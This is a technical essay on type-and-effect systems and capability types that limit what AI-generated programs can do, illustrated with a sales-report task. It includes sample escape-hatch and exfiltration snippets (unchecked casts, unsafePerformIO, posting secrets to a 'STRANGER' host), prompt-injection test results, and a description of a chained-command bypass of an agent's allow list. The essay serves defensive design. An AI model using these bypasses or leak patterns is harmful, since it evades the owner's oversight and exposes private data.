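A Haskell function with an ordinary type can still fail or run forever, so Zhou and colleagues go too far when they write that expecting a whole number also rules out exceptions. Koka, like Fox, uses `pure` for functions that can fail or run forever, and Koka's manual, quoted by a user in the Haskell forum thread *Why use an effect system?*, explains that this corresponds to Haskell's idea of purity. The calculator could therefore still crash or hang, but it couldn't delete anything.

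Koka's list distinguishes these cases. In the Microsoft slides, which show the language as it was in 2012, `io` combines reading global memory, writing it, running forever, raising exceptions and giving unpredictable results, but none of these separates files from the network. A manager could learn from Koka's types that a function might crash, which Haskell's types can't show, but not whether it might send the sales figures somewhere. Koka is also still a research language, and Leijen (2024) warns in *The Koka Programming Language* that it isn't ready for production use.

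Flix comes closest to the small list. Its current manual describes separate effects for many operations, including reading files, writing files, checking file details such as size, making web requests, running processes, using the console, reading environment variables, reading the clock and sleeping. The categories have changed, though. Madsen's slides, *Effectful Programming in the Flix Programming Language*, list eight primitive effects, including `FsRead`, `FsWrite`, `Net` and `Exec`. The current page on primitive effects, which is marked as awaiting a rewrite, describes only `IO` and `NonDet` (for functions that may return different results each time), and most of the finer distinctions are now in the standard library. Grants written in Flix's terms should therefore also specify the language version.

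It is still easy to grant the catch-all `IO` effect by accident. A small program in Flix's manual that counts the words in a file has the effects {FileRead, IO}, and it needs `IO` only because it prints the result with the ordinary `println`. A grant copied from that signature would allow far more than printing. For example, Flix's library includes a default handler for `FileWrite`, which is code that carries out the effect's operations and turns the effect into `IO`. A program could write to a file, apply this handler itself, and still have only {FileRead, IO} in its signature. Printing through the separate `Console` effect avoids the problem, so a system for generated programs should offer `Console` and leave `IO` out of every grant.

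Hack, which grew out of the web language PHP, attaches named sets of permissions, called contexts, to function types. A function may call another only if it has every permission the other needs. HHVM's *Available Contexts & Capabilities* describes four permissions for general use. `IO` covers only two commands that print text, and the other three concern objects and global variables. All remaining permissions are for Meta's internal use or no longer in use. The only context for general use that includes `IO` is `defaults`, which also allows a function to change objects and global variables. Hack can therefore confirm that a function only computes, but it has no separate permission for reading a file or for contacting a server.

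Epic Games created the language Verse for building games. *EVerseEffectSet*, a reference page for the company's game engine, lists seven effects: waiting, failing, running forever, reading memory, writing memory, creating objects, and doing something that can't be undone. The last reflects Verse's unusual ability to roll back the changes that part of a program made to memory when that part fails. Marking what can't be undone would be useful for the sales program too, since nobody can recall a message to the accounts department, but it would put posting a total and leaking the customer list in the same category.

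Solidity is a language for programs that run on Ethereum, a blockchain (a record of transactions that many computers share). A `view` function may read the blockchain's data but not change it, and a `pure` function may do neither. Checking the current block's time counts as reading, so a `pure` function can't behave differently after a certain date. Sending money counts as a change, so neither kind of function can pay anyone. The two keywords forbid few kinds of actions, but these include the main harms that a program on a blockchain can do.

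Verse has seven effects, but checking them would rule out almost nothing that worries the manager. Haskell has a single type for side effects, so the manager could stop every leak and deletion, but only by refusing all side effects. Of the six type systems, only Flix's would let the manager approve the sales program and refuse the version that deletes its input.

### When programmers declare too much

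Programmers can write imprecise declarations even in a language with precise categories. Java's checked exceptions are a well-known example. If a Java method might raise one of these exceptions, such as the one for a failed file operation, it must either catch the exception or name it in its declaration. If the method declares the exception, every method that calls it must also catch or declare it. Programmers can avoid listing specific exceptions by writing `throws Exception`, which covers every checked exception. The compiler accepts this even on a method that raises none, so callers learn only that something might go wrong.

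Java also lacks a convenient form of effect polymorphism for exceptions. Its standard `map` accepts only functions that declare no checked exceptions. A programmer who wants to read a file for each item in a list has to catch the exception inside the function, and often replaces it with an unchecked one, which the compiler does not check. Checked exceptions therefore have a poor reputation partly because Java's system lacks effect variables, so that reputation is weaker evidence against languages that have them.

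Declaring too much is also less attractive when the declaration has to fit a grant. A Java programmer can write `throws Exception` and the program will compile, leaving other people to deal with the consequences. But if a model declares all four categories for the sales program, it is refused because the grant has only two. The person tempted to allow too much is then whoever sets the grant, as happened with Java's `AllPermission`.

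In Java, a method that catches an exception no longer has to declare it, and programmers can write an empty handler just to satisfy the compiler. Koka's type for catching exceptions works the same way. If an action may raise an exception and has other effects, catching the exception leaves only the other effects in the type. This is right for exceptions because the handler stops them, but a handler can't undo an effect such as sending a message. Flix doesn't let programs handle its primitive effects, and a handler for a library effect such as `FileWrite` replaces that effect with the effects of its own code. A handler that keeps the text in memory writes nothing to disk, while one that writes a real file adds `IO` to the type.

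The trouble of keeping declarations up to date does carry over. If a library function deep in a program starts writing a log, every function that calls it gains `FileWrite`, and programmers must change each handwritten declaration. Giving every function the broadest effect avoids these updates, but Flix's manual warns against it, showing a guessing game in which all five functions have `IO`, so that "every function can do anything".

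Inference removes much of the work of declaring effects, but it also matters how a language treats a missing declaration. In Hack, a function without one gets `defaults`, a broad set of permissions, according to HHVM's *Introduction*. Similarly, a Verse function that names no main effect gets `no_rollback`, according to Epic Games' *Specifiers and attributes in Verse*. Flix treats a named function without a declaration as having no effects, so the compiler reports an error if the function prints anything. The Flix default suits generated code better because a forgotten declaration leads to a compiler error rather than extra permissions.

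### What the guarantee depends on

This checking is useful only if it is sound, meaning that when the checker concludes `e : T \ E`, no run of `e` has an effect outside `E`. Researchers can prove this for a small mathematical model of a language. *Koka programming with row polymorphic effect types* makes the same claim about uncaught exceptions as Grossman's lecture notes. For security, Flix's developers promise "iron-clad guarantees", including that a function without effects can't reach the file system or the network.

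The proof covers only the language in the model, and practical languages usually add an escape hatch, a feature that lets code act without the effect check seeing it. Madsen's slides state that programmers can't subvert Flix's type and effect system, and show the compiler rejecting a function that claims to have no effects but prints a greeting. Flix's manual, however, describes a feature that makes the same trick work:

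```
unchecked_cast(println("Hello World") as _ \ {})
```

This prints the text, but the cast makes the compiler treat the expression as having no side effects. The manual calls such casts extremely dangerous and says that programmers should normally never need one. That advice is enough for colleagues, but a generated program could wrap `delete_file("sales.csv")` in the same cast, and the checker would again find only {FileRead, Net}.

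A program can also get around the check by calling code in another language. Flix programs can use any Java library, but the compiler can't work out from Java's types what a Java method does to the outside world. It has to rely on effects that somebody assigned to the method or that the programmer declares.

Flix deals with both problems by building each package that a program depends on in one of three security contexts:

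| Context | Calls to Java | Unchecked casts | `IO` |
|---|---|---|---|
| `paranoid` | Forbidden | Forbidden | Forbidden |
| `plain` (the default) | Forbidden | Forbidden | Allowed |
| `unrestricted` | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |

A package can't get around its context's restrictions by depending on a less restricted package, because those restrictions also apply to everything it depends on. According to the manual, in the `unrestricted` context a reader can't infer anything from a function's declared effects about what the code may do.

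The contexts apply only to packages. Flix always leaves a project's own code unrestricted, so pasting the generated sales program into the project would let it use casts and Java. Whoever runs it should put it in a separate package, build that package as `paranoid`, and call it from a short, trusted program that people wrote. The generated code could still use named effects such as `FileRead` and `Http`, but not `IO`, and the trusted program would define how to carry them out.

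### Taking the escape hatches out of Haskell

Haskell programmers have dealt with this problem for years. The language's best-known escape hatch is a function called `unsafePerformIO`, which takes an action of type `IO` and returns its result as an ordinary value:

```
unsafePerformIO : IO a -> a
```

A dishonest version of `to_number` could use it to send each line of the sales file to a stranger and then return the right amount. Its type would still be a function from text to a number. Every calculation that used `to_number` would look free of effects, and so would the AI calculator if the model wrote the same trick there.

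Safe Haskell is a restricted form of Haskell that leaves out `unsafePerformIO` and similar features. A compiler setting turns it on, so whoever runs the generated code can enforce the restriction without relying on the model to avoid those features. Zhou and colleagues use Safe Haskell for this reason.

Banning one function by name wouldn't be enough, because the program could import a library that uses it internally. Banning every such library would exclude some that use the function harmlessly, for example to make a calculation faster. Safe Haskell therefore divides the modules that safe code may import into two groups. GHC's *Safe Haskell*, part of the manual for the main Haskell compiler, explains that the compiler makes sure modules marked `Safe` use no unsafe features. A module marked `Trustworthy` may use unsafe features internally, but its author vouches that nobody can misuse them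 from outside. The compiler doesn't check this claim and places few restrictions on the module.

Anyone, including a model, can write `Trustworthy` at the top of a file. The manual calls unrestricted use of the mark a problem and recommends a setting called `-fpackage-trust`. With this setting, the compiler trusts a module marked `Trustworthy` only if the person compiling the program has also chosen to trust the package that contains it. For the sales program, that person would compile the generated code as `Safe` and trust only the packages needed to read files and send requests. The amount of code that someone must read carefully then depends on the size of those packages, not on how many programs the model writes.

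Safe Haskell prevents code from bypassing its types, but a program of type `IO` can still delete files because that type allows it. To let the sales program read and post but not delete, someone would have to give it a more restricted type, which Haskell's libraries make possible.

Type checking also offers no protection while the compiler is running. A Haskell source file can make the GHC compiler run another program on it before checking the types, so a malicious file could do its damage before the check is finished. Flix's manual warns that merely building a program with unrestricted packages can expose a computer to attack. The compiler should therefore run in a sandbox too, with no access to the sales figures and no network connection.

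## Making a grant more precise without adding categories

The grant {FileRead, Net} stops the sales program from deleting its input but still lets it read the payroll and send it to a stranger. Adding categories wouldn't prevent this, because reading the payroll and reading `sales.csv` are both file reads. A grant can separate them using the same four categories, either by limiting which files and hosts a category covers or by letting a library build narrower permissions from the broad ones.

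### One folder and one host

A scoped grant pairs each category with the resources it covers. For the sales program it might be:

```
FileRead : files under /reports
Net      : accounts.example
```

The system permits an operation only if the grant includes the operation's category and the file or host is within that category's scope. A manager who already understands "read files" only has to learn a folder's name to understand a grant limited to that folder.

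Scopes can remove far more excess authority than extra categories can. Suppose, as in the earlier illustration, that the computer holds 5,000 files, 12 of them in `/reports`, and the library has 8 operations that read files. An unlimited `FileRead` permits 8 × 5,000 = 40,000 combinations of operation and file. If the designer split `FileRead` into eight categories, one per operation, and the manager granted one of them, 5,000 combinations would remain, including one that reads the payroll. Limiting the original `FileRead` to `/reports` would leave 8 × 12 = 96 combinations, none of which reads the payroll.

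A compiler can check only part of a scoped grant. It can't always determine which file a program will open, because the program may build the file's name as it runs, for instance from the current month. The usual solution is to use types to ensure that the program reaches files and hosts only through a particular library, which compares each path or address with the scope at run time. The software company VirtusLab, in its guide to restricting AI-written Scala code, gives the example of a web client that connects only to hosts on an approved list. A program can therefore pass the compiler's check and still fail at run time because it tries to connect to a host that isn't on the list.

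The run-time comparison is easy to get wrong. The path `/reports/../payroll/june.csv` begins with the permitted folder but leads out of it, because `..` means the folder above. A symbolic link, an entry in one folder that points to a file somewhere else, can do the same even when the path looks ordinary. The library has to work out where a path leads before comparing it with the scope.

If the grant names one fixed file, types alone can enforce it. Whoever runs the sales program creates a value, `sales`, whose `read` operation takes no path and always opens `sales.csv`. A program that holds `sales` and has no other way to open files can't express a request for the payroll. A program that has to process whatever files it finds in a folder still needs the run-time check.

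A scope limits where an operation acts but not what it does there. A program with `FileWrite` limited to `/reports` could still erase all 12 reports, so scoped grants must also separate reading from writing.

### Effects that a library defines

Wyvern, a research language designed with security in mind, lets programmers define an effect in terms of lower-level ones. *l6 capabilities for effects*, a set of lecture slides, includes this definition:

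```
effect write = {File.write, Socket.write}
```

A socket is an open network connection, so a function with the effect `write` may write to a file, the network, or both. The definition of `write` can belong to an object, alongside the object's functions, and is then called an effect member.

Suppose the accounts department publishes a library with its own effect, `report`, and one function that has it:

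```
send_total : Number -> Text \ {report}
```

The manager wants to grant {FileRead, report}, so that the program can send a total but can't use `post` to send anything else. But if the library defines `report` as {Net}, the checker will treat the two names as equal and accept a program that calls `post` directly. If the library hides the definition, the checker will treat the names as different, but the manager can't find out whether `report` includes starting processes.

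Wyvern's answer is to publish a bound instead of a definition. Melicher, Xu and colleagues (2022), in *Bounded Abstract Effects*, describe effect members with upper and lower bounds. An upper bound for the accounts library would be

report ⊆ {Net}

From this the checker can conclude that `send_total` starts no processes and writes no files. It can't conclude that everything in `Net` fits within `report`, so it rejects a program that calls `post`. A lower bound, {Net} ⊆ report, would allow that conclusion. Lower bounds are useful when a library accepts functions from other people's code and the checker must verify that their effects fit, but in a grant this one would again let the program call `post`.

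An upper bound also makes changes to the library visible. If the accounts department starts keeping a local copy of every report, `send_total` gains `FileWrite`, and the library won't compile until someone widens the bound. Linux administrators got no such warning when developers added new powers to an existing capability. The manager's system should still store the bound with the grant. Otherwise, an old approval of `report` would silently cover the wider version.

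Melicher and colleagues note that many exception systems offer such hierarchies, because one class of error can be a special case of another, but that general effect systems rarely do. Their formal model can be used to reason about attenuation, which is handing out a weaker version of a power, as the accounts library does here.

A limit can hold even if the generated code has no effect labels. Craig, Potanin and colleagues (2017) consider a logger that appends to a file and an unlabelled client that holds the logger, and ask what effects the client might have. Wyvern is capability-safe, so code can act only through objects that other code has given it, and the client can do only what the logger allows to the file. The slides add that if a function is labelled `write` but nothing available to the code can write to a socket, the checker can drop `Socket.write` from its estimate. Similarly,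 a sales program that receives only `send_total` and a reader for `sales.csv` has at most the effects {FileRead, report}, even if it has no effect labels.

In *A case study in language-based security*, Fish, Melicher and Aldrich (2020) used Wyvern's security features to build a small standard library for input and output. They wanted to find out whether the features are practical, and to make a library that other programmers would find harder to misuse. They combined capability safety and effects with a language extension that guards against command injection, in which an attacker inserts extra commands into text that a program passes on for execution. Two of the three also worked on the effect system, so the study shows that people who know Wyvern well can build such a library with it. It provides little evidence of how well programmers new to the language, or models trained on hardly any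 Wyvern code, would do.

### A type for one task

Haskell's `IO` type permits every kind of contact with the outside world, but a library can offer a narrower type in its place. ELBA, the system that runs a generated Haskell program only if it has the expected type, relies on this. Zhou and colleagues use the example of an agent that compiles bibliographies. They want every entry to come from DBLP, an online database of computer science publications, so they define a type called `BibIO` that permits three operations:

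| Operation | What it does |
|---|---|
| `dblpSearch` | Finds papers that match a request |
| `dblpFetchBib` | Fetches the entry for one paper |
| `appendToBibFile` | Adds an entry to a file |

A program of type `BibIO` can combine these with any amount of ordinary calculation, such as sorting the papers by year. It can't call Haskell's general `writeFile`, which has type `IO`.

`BibIO` by itself would let the model make up an entry and append it. The library prevents this with a second type, `Trusted Bib`. Only `dblpFetchBib` produces values of this type, and `appendToBibFile` accepts no other type. The generated code can't create such a value itself because the library keeps the constructor private.

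An ordinary tool could enforce the same rule by fetching an entry and appending it in a single step. But the model would then have to look at the entries one at a time to find the earliest paper on a subject, instead of writing a line of code that compares them. In a test with 100 topics, none of the 925 citations that ELBA's agent produced had the wrong authors, year or identifier, compared with 19 of the 1,002 from a conventional agent using the same model. The types may not account for the whole difference, because ELBA's agent copied its entries from a database while the other wrote them from web searches and memory. A conventional agent with the single-step tool might have done just as well.

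For the sales program, a type called `SalesIO` could permit two operations:

```
read_sales : SalesIO Text
send_total : Number -> SalesIO Text
```

Neither operation takes a path or an address, so the program can't choose another file or recipient. Because `send_total` accepts only a number, the program can't paste the customer list into its message, although it could encode a name as a very long number. The manager reads two lines, which describe the task more precisely than {FileRead, Net} does.

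ELBA's programs can request more code from the model while they run, but the same limit applies to that code. A request inside a `SalesIO` program must produce either another `SalesIO` program or something stricter, such as a plain number. If the program requests code of type `IO`, the compiler rejects it.

Some tasks need a whole folder. For these, Zhou and colleagues define `RIO`, whose operations require a special `Path` value where most libraries accept text:

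```
readRIO  : Path -> RIO Text
writeRIO : Path -> Text -> RIO ()
```

The empty brackets mean that `writeRIO` returns nothing useful. Whoever starts the program supplies the first `Path`, for `/reports`, and the program can derive narrower ones from it, such as `root // "sales.csv"`. The `Path` is the authority over the folder, and a program without one can't read or write anything.

If the program calls `readRIO "/payroll/june.csv"`, the compiler rejects it because text is not a `Path`. The expression `root // "../payroll/june.csv"` compiles, but at run time the `//` operation resolves the path and any symbolic links, and rejects the result because it is outside `/reports`.

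This is more reliable than checking the text of commands, as many coding agents do, because with `RIO` there is no command text to misread. Zhou and colleagues cite a fault reported in Claude Code in March 2026. The agent compared only the first command with its list, so a user could get a forbidden command past the rules by adding it after a permitted one with `&&`.

In `RIO`, the same `Path` works for both `readRIO` and `writeRIO`, so a sales program that can read `sales.csv` can also overwrite it. Separate types for readable and writable paths would fix this.

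### Capabilities that appear in types

Scala 3 has an experimental feature called capture checking, which records in the type of each value the capabilities that the value can use. Suppose `sales` is a capability for reading one file and `accounts` is a capability for posting to one server. Three short functions would then have these types:

```
() => sales.read()            : () ->{sales} Text
text => accounts.post(text)   : Text ->{accounts} Text
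text => split_lines(text)     : Text -> List of Text
```

The names in braces form the function's capture set. An effect system would give the first function the effect `FileRead`, which covers every file on the machine. Scala instead puts the variable `sales`, which stands for one file, in the capture set. A program with twenty files can have twenty such names without anyone listing them in advance.

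Like E, a capture set is an upper estimate. The third function has an empty set, so it is pure. It can't read a file or post a message, because it would need a capability to do either. Requiring a pure function for one part of a program also helps protect secret data.

Capture sets support hierarchies much like Wyvern's. If a library builds an object `reporter` from `sales` and `accounts`, the compiler records that {reporter} fits within {sales, accounts}. Code can then mention only `reporter` in its types, and the compiler can still determine which resources `reporter` may use.

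Earlier capability systems were awkward because each function had to receive every capability that it, or anything it called, might need. Scala can pass these capabilities implicitly. It also avoids most of the notation that effect polymorphism usually requires, because its ordinary function arrow, `=>`, already means a function that may use any capability. In *What's in the Box*, Xu, Bračevac and colleagues (2025) converted Scala's standard collections library, about 30,000 lines, to capture checking. They changed less than 5% of the lines, and almost 90% of the function signatures stayed the same, including that of `map`.

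An earlier version of the checker couldn't handle capabilities stored inside collections, and the first attempts to fix this made it unsound. Xu and colleagues designed a new foundation and proved it sound with Lean, a program that checks mathematical proofs. The proof supports the design, but mistakes in the compiler could still let bad code through.

### Why a file handle can't leave its block

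Capture checking can also limit how long a program keeps a capability. Suppose `request_folder` creates a capability for a folder, passes it to a block of code, and cancels it when the block ends. A program might try to keep its access like this:

```
read_later = request_folder("/reports", folder =>
    () => folder.read("sales.csv"))
```

The block only returns a function that would read the file later, after the access should have ended. The function's type is `() ->{folder} Text`, so the type of `read_later` would have to mention `folder` too. But `folder` exists only inside the block, so the compiler can't give `read_later` a valid type and rejects the program. Putting the function in a list or storing it in an outside variable doesn't help, because the type of the list or variable would also have to mention `folder`.

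If the block returns the contents of the file instead, the program passes, because text is ordinary data and carries no capability. The block limits how long the program can read the folder, but what the program has already read can go anywhere its other capabilities allow.

### Scala's safe mode

All of this depends on the compiler seeing every use of a capability, and ordinary Scala has escape hatches that hide them. Safe mode removes these with six restrictions, which Odersky and colleagues list:

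1. The code can't use unchecked casts or pattern matches, which treat a value as having a type that the compiler hasn't verified.
2. It can't use anything from `caps.unsafe`, a module of deliberately unsafe features.
3. It can't use the `@unchecked` annotation, which switches off some of the compiler's checks.
4. It can't use reflection, which looks up and calls parts of a program by name at run time.
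5. It has to compile with capture checking on, including the tracking of every change to stored data, and with strict rules for missing values.
6. It can use a global object or function only if that object or function is itself implemented safely.

The first four keep a program from hiding a capability it holds. The sixth matters at least as much for the sales program, which could otherwise call Java's file library and delete `sales.csv` without holding any capability.

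Some code still has to open files directly, and a library author can mark it `@assumeSafe`. Like Haskell's `Trustworthy`, this mark makes the compiler accept the author's claim that the code is safe without verifying it. VirtusLab points out in its guide that safe code can't contain the mark, so a model can't use it to exempt its own program from the checks. VirtusLab also reports that safe mode was available only in Scala's nightly builds, which are unfinished versions released for testing. Odersky and colleagues call Scala 3 the only production-ready language that tracks capabilities in types, which is a fair description of the language but overstates how ready these two features are.

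### Requests for files, hosts and commands

TACIT, the system that Odersky and colleagues built on safe mode, receives Scala code from an agent, compiles it, and runs it only if it passes. The code reaches the outside world through a library with three kinds of request:

| Request | What the program names | What it may then do |
|---|---|---|
| `requestFileSystem` | A folder | List, read, write, append to and delete files in it |
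| `requestNetwork` | A set of hosts | Fetch pages from them and post data to them |
| `requestExecPermission` | A set of commands | Run those commands |

The sales program would make two requests:

```
val total = requestFileSystem("/reports") {
  addUp(access("/reports/sales.csv").readLines())
}
requestNetwork(Set("accounts.example")) {
  httpPost("https://accounts.example/totals",
           s"Total sales: $total")
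}
```

The compiler checks that the program opens files only inside the first block and posts only inside the second. The library checks the path and the host at run time. By the time the program contacts the accounts department, it has lost access to the folder. If the agent continues in a later step, it has to request that access again.

The file request covers a single folder, but the same handle allows both reading and deleting, so the version of the sales program that deletes its input would compile and run. TACIT's users can change the library without changing the rest of the system, and a read-only file request would be a sensible first addition.

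It also matters who chooses the scope. In these calls the generated program names the folder and the hosts itself, and a program that named `/payroll` and a stranger's server would satisfy the type checker just as well. OpenBSD's `pledge` has the same limitation when a program chooses its own promises. The person running the code needs a library that compares each request with an outside grant, or else has to create the capabilities beforehand. The job-specific part of the policy that Odersky and colleagues wrote for comparing contracts does the latter, and the sales version might be:

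```
object Environment {
  val sales    = ReadOnlyFile("/reports/sales.csv")
  val accounts = Recipient("https://accounts.example/totals")
}
```

The generated program can use these two values but can't create others like them. Traditional capability languages forbid such global values because any code could use them. Scala can allow them because the type of every function that uses `sales` or `accounts` includes that name.

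Commands are the weakest of the three. A command that the program launches runs outside Scala, so the types no longer limit it and the only protection left is the list of permitted commands. One example in TACIT's documentation requests `pip` and `python`, which permits as much as the Python rules that Claude Code's users wrote. Odersky and colleagues recommend permitting only specific safe commands, such as `git diff` and `sbt`, and adding a sandbox where security is critical. But `sbt`, which builds Scala projects, runs code from their build files, so a program that can also edit those files can make it run almost anything.

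### Permissions from the surrounding code

A person can also write most of a program and leave a gap for the model to fill. Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, take this approach, again in Scala. The manager's programmer might write:

```
def monthlyTotal(sales: ReadOnlyFile): Double =
  agent("add up the last column of the sales file")
```

When the program reaches the call to `agent`, the model writes code for that spot. The compiler checks the code as though the programmer had typed it there, so it can use only the variables visible at that point and must produce a number. If the check fails, none of the code runs, and the model gets the error messages and tries again.

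With capture checking and safe mode on, the variables visible to the generated code determine its permissions. Here the only capability among them is `sales`, so the generated code can read the file but cannot post anything. The programmer's own code can send the result to the accounts department without letting the model choose the address. The grant needs no separate policy file, and a reviewer can see it in the function's first line.

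The weakness of this design is that programs usually have more variables in scope than any one task needs. If the programmer put the same gap in the middle of a long function that also handled the payroll, the generated code could use the payroll too. Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that the compiler enforces whatever scope the developer provides but doesn't work out the smallest one. Moving each gap into a short function with few parameters is an easy precaution. Gaps inside generated code need the same attention, because the code that fills them can use everything visible to the surrounding code, including any variables the surrounding code has added.

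### What the extra precision costs

Applied to the sales program, these designs rule out different things:

| Grant | Delete `sales.csv` | Read the payroll | Post to a stranger | Send customer names to accounts |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| {FileRead, Net} | Refused | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |
| The same, with scopes | Refused | Refused | Refused | Allowed |
| {FileRead, report} | Refused | Allowed | Refused | Only encoded as a number |
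| `SalesIO` | Refused | Refused | Refused | Only encoded as a number |
| TACIT's requests, with the folder and host fixed from outside | Allowed | Refused | Refused | Allowed |

`SalesIO` is the most restrictive, but someone has to write it, as with any interface made for one kind of task. Odersky and colleagues report about 1,000 lines for the part of TACIT that all agents share, and a few hundred more for each domain, such as airline bookings or retail orders. The domain code is about as long as the tool descriptions it replaces, so an organisation that already maintains such descriptions may not find the code much extra work. Models can help draft it, though people should review the result. Only the shared part requires much knowledge of capture checking.

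All of this code has to be correct, because the compiler can't detect when a permission allows more than its author intended. If `send_total` accepted text by mistake, every program that used it would still pass the check. With ten domains of 300 lines each, an organisation would have 4,000 lines to trust, however many programs the model writes.

New names make grants harder to review. Someone who has learned four categories can read any grant made from them, with or without scopes. `BibIO`, `SalesIO` and `report` each need an explanation, and a familiar-looking name can mislead, as Android's headings did. For example, another team's `SalesIO` might well allow a program to change sales records.

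Task-specific types also make grants harder to compare. {FileRead} is plainly narrower than {FileRead, Net}, as is access to `/reports/june` than access to `/reports`, but to compare two task-specific types, someone has to read what each of their operations does. Suppose an attacker takes over the accounts department's server, and an administrator needs to find every program that can contact it. With scoped grants, the administrator can search for the server's name, but with fifty task-specific types, they have to read fifty interfaces.

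Upper bounds can restore some of this. Each interface would declare an upper bound on what it can do, using the four categories and their scopes. For `SalesIO`, the bound would be `FileRead` on `sales.csv` and `Net` to `accounts.example`. Administrators could then search and compare the bounds, while the compiler checked programs against the narrower type. The bound omits some details, such as the rule that `send_total` accepts only a number, but administrators could still use it to find the programs that can reach a given server.

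For a sales report that runs once, scopes are probably the best choice, since two extra lines in the grant keep the program away from the payroll and from strangers' servers. A task-specific type is worth the effort when many generated programs do the same kind of work, or when the content of a message matters as well as the operations and their destinations.

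## Stopping data leaks that use only permitted effects

A grant of {FileRead, Net} can't stop a program from reading `sales.csv` and posting the customers' names instead of the total. Odersky and colleagues point out that a sandbox doesn't stop this leak either. The sandbox lets the program read the file and contact the server, and the data passes from the file to the server without crossing the sandbox's boundary.

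More categories wouldn't help, because the honest program and the leaking one can differ in a single argument:

```
post(ACCOUNTS_ADDRESS, to_text(total))
post(ACCOUNTS_ADDRESS, text)
```

Even if every operation had its own category, both programs would have the same E, because E doesn't record which value reaches `post`. It doesn't record order either, so a program that posts "starting" before reading the file has the same E as one that reads first.

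The manager could refuse any grant that contains both categories, but this would also stop the sales program. If the job is split between a program that only reads and one that only posts, data can still leak through whatever the first program passes to the second. A program may also leak data without `Net`. If it prints the customer list to an agent that runs on a cloud model, the agent sends the list to the company that operates the model. *LLMEffect* (Sen, 2026) proposes a type system that puts security labels on data going into such model calls.

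The manager wants a property close to what researchers call noninterference. *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions* (Stefan, Russo and colleagues, 2012) defines it as the rule that publicly readable results must not depend on secret inputs. If somebody changed the secret file and ran the program again, an outsider should see the same output. The sales program can't meet this standard if the accounts department counts as an outsider, because the total changes with the sales. Somebody therefore has to decide that the accounts department may know the total.

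### A container for secret data

TACIT, the system that checks an agent's Scala code, can wrap the contents of secret files in a container called `Classified`. Generated code can't take the contents out. It can only pass the container's `map` operation a function to apply to them, and the result comes back in a new container. Capture checking, which records in a function's type what the function can reach, lets `map` accept only functions without side effects. The sales program could add up a secret file like this:

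```
val total = requestFileSystem("/reports") {
  val text = access("/reports/sales.csv").readClassified()
  text.map(t => addUp(t))
}
```

The compiler accepts `addUp` because it only calculates. It would reject `text.map(t => httpPost(STRANGER, t))` because the function passed to `map` uses the network. It would also reject a function that opens a file there.

The total is now in a container too. If the program tries to post it as ordinary text, the code compiles, but the message reads "Total sales: Classified(\*\*\*\*)", because converting the container to text always produces that placeholder. To carry out the manager's decision to release the real figure, someone has to add a trusted operation, perhaps called `sendTotal`, that accepts a classified number and posts it only to the accounts department.

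Printing works similarly. The user's terminal shows the real contents and the agent gets the asterisks, so the text never reaches the cloud model. For work that needs a model, such as summarising a secret report, TACIT can pass the container to a separate model that the organisation trusts, and the summary comes back wrapped. Type checking can't guarantee that this second model doesn't retain the data, so its operator has to ensure that.

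Odersky and colleagues tested the container on a sample software project with a folder of access keys, a database and confidential documents. They paired 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections, which ranged from instructions in code comments to ready-made Scala code for reading the secret files. They added 11 malicious requests, 5 that asked for secrets outright and 6 in which the user posed as someone entitled to them. This made 131 trials for each model, which they ran once with the container and once with the secrets as plain text. The table gives the share of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output:

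| Model | Trials | With the container | Without it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 with injections | 100% | 100% |
| | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% |
| | All 131 | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 with injections | 100% | 97.5% |
| | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 27.3% |
| | All 131 | 100% | 91.6% |

Without the container, preventing leaks depended entirely on the model refusing. Sonnet leaked secrets in 2 of the 11 malicious trials and MiniMax in 8.

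The researchers designed this test to measure the property that their types are meant to guarantee, so they should have expected a perfect score. On its own, no leak in 131 trials would be compatible with a true leak rate of about 2%. The compiler's rule is stronger evidence, and the trials mainly show that the implementation has no obvious hole. A grant that kept the agent out of the secret folder would also have prevented these leaks, but then the agent couldn't have summarised a confidential incident report or anonymised employee reviews, as it did here. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the ordinary tasks with the container and 83.3% without it, while MiniMax completed 90.0% with it and 88.3% without it. Sonnet's lower score without the container may be an artifact, since it often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

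They also ran TACIT on AgentDojo, a benchmark built by other researchers, in which agents do banking, office, Slack and travel tasks while attackers hide instructions in the data. Most of that data, such as e-mails and bank transactions, arrives in containers. One of the 1,926 attacks across two models succeeded by the benchmark's count. In that case, the agent booked the hotel the user wanted but quoted its reviews, where the attacker had inserted a recommendation for another hotel. The attack counted as successful because the answer contained the other hotel's name, although the user was allowed to see the reviews.

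### Labels that follow the data

A program can also carry a label that records what kinds of data it has read, and the system can check that label whenever the program sends something. ELBA, which runs generated Haskell only if it has the expected type, does this with LIO, an existing Haskell library by Stefan and colleagues. The types restrict the program to LIO's operations, which check the labels at run time.

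In a simplified version, a label is a set of data sources. The program starts with an empty label L. When it reads data with label D, the system updates L:

L := L ∪ D

Each destination has a label W for the data it may receive, and the program may send to it only if

L ⊆ W

Suppose the accounts department may receive sales data and a stranger's server may receive only public data. A program could then run as follows:

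| Step | L after the step | Outcome |
|---|---|---|
| Fetch exchange rates from a public site | {} | Allowed |
| Read `sales.csv` | {sales} | Allowed |
| Post the total to accounts | {sales} | Allowed |
| Post the total to a stranger | {sales} | Refused |
| Read the payroll | {sales, payroll} | Allowed |
| Post the total to accounts again | {sales, payroll} | Refused |

Unlike E, the label takes order into account, so fetching the exchange rates would fail if the program had already read the sales file. But it doesn't separate the total from the customers' names. Both come from `sales.csv`, so the accounts department could receive either unless someone gave the names their own label.

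The last refusal is unnecessary, because the program worked out the total before it opened the payroll. LIO normally keeps one label for everything the program holds. *Cryptographically Secure Information Flow Control on Key-Value Stores* (2017), which builds on LIO, explains that this label, once raised, can't be lowered within the same computation. An agent that works through many sources may therefore end up unable to send anything. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls the general problem label explosion: every piece of data ends up with the same label, "everything".

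LIO has two features that help. The first, `toLabeled`, runs part of a program separately and returns the result sealed under its own label, without changing the label of the rest. A program could process the payroll this way and still report the sales. The second, clearance, is an upper limit on L. With a clearance of {sales}, the program would fail when it tried to read the payroll, before it had any payroll data to leak.

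ELBA's labels also limit prompt injection by recording integrity, meaning which sources have influenced the data. When a model reads text from an untrusted source, ELBA's policy reduces the model's privileges to those of the source. If a customer writes a comment in `sales.csv` telling the model to post the file somewhere, the model can do so only if the customer could.

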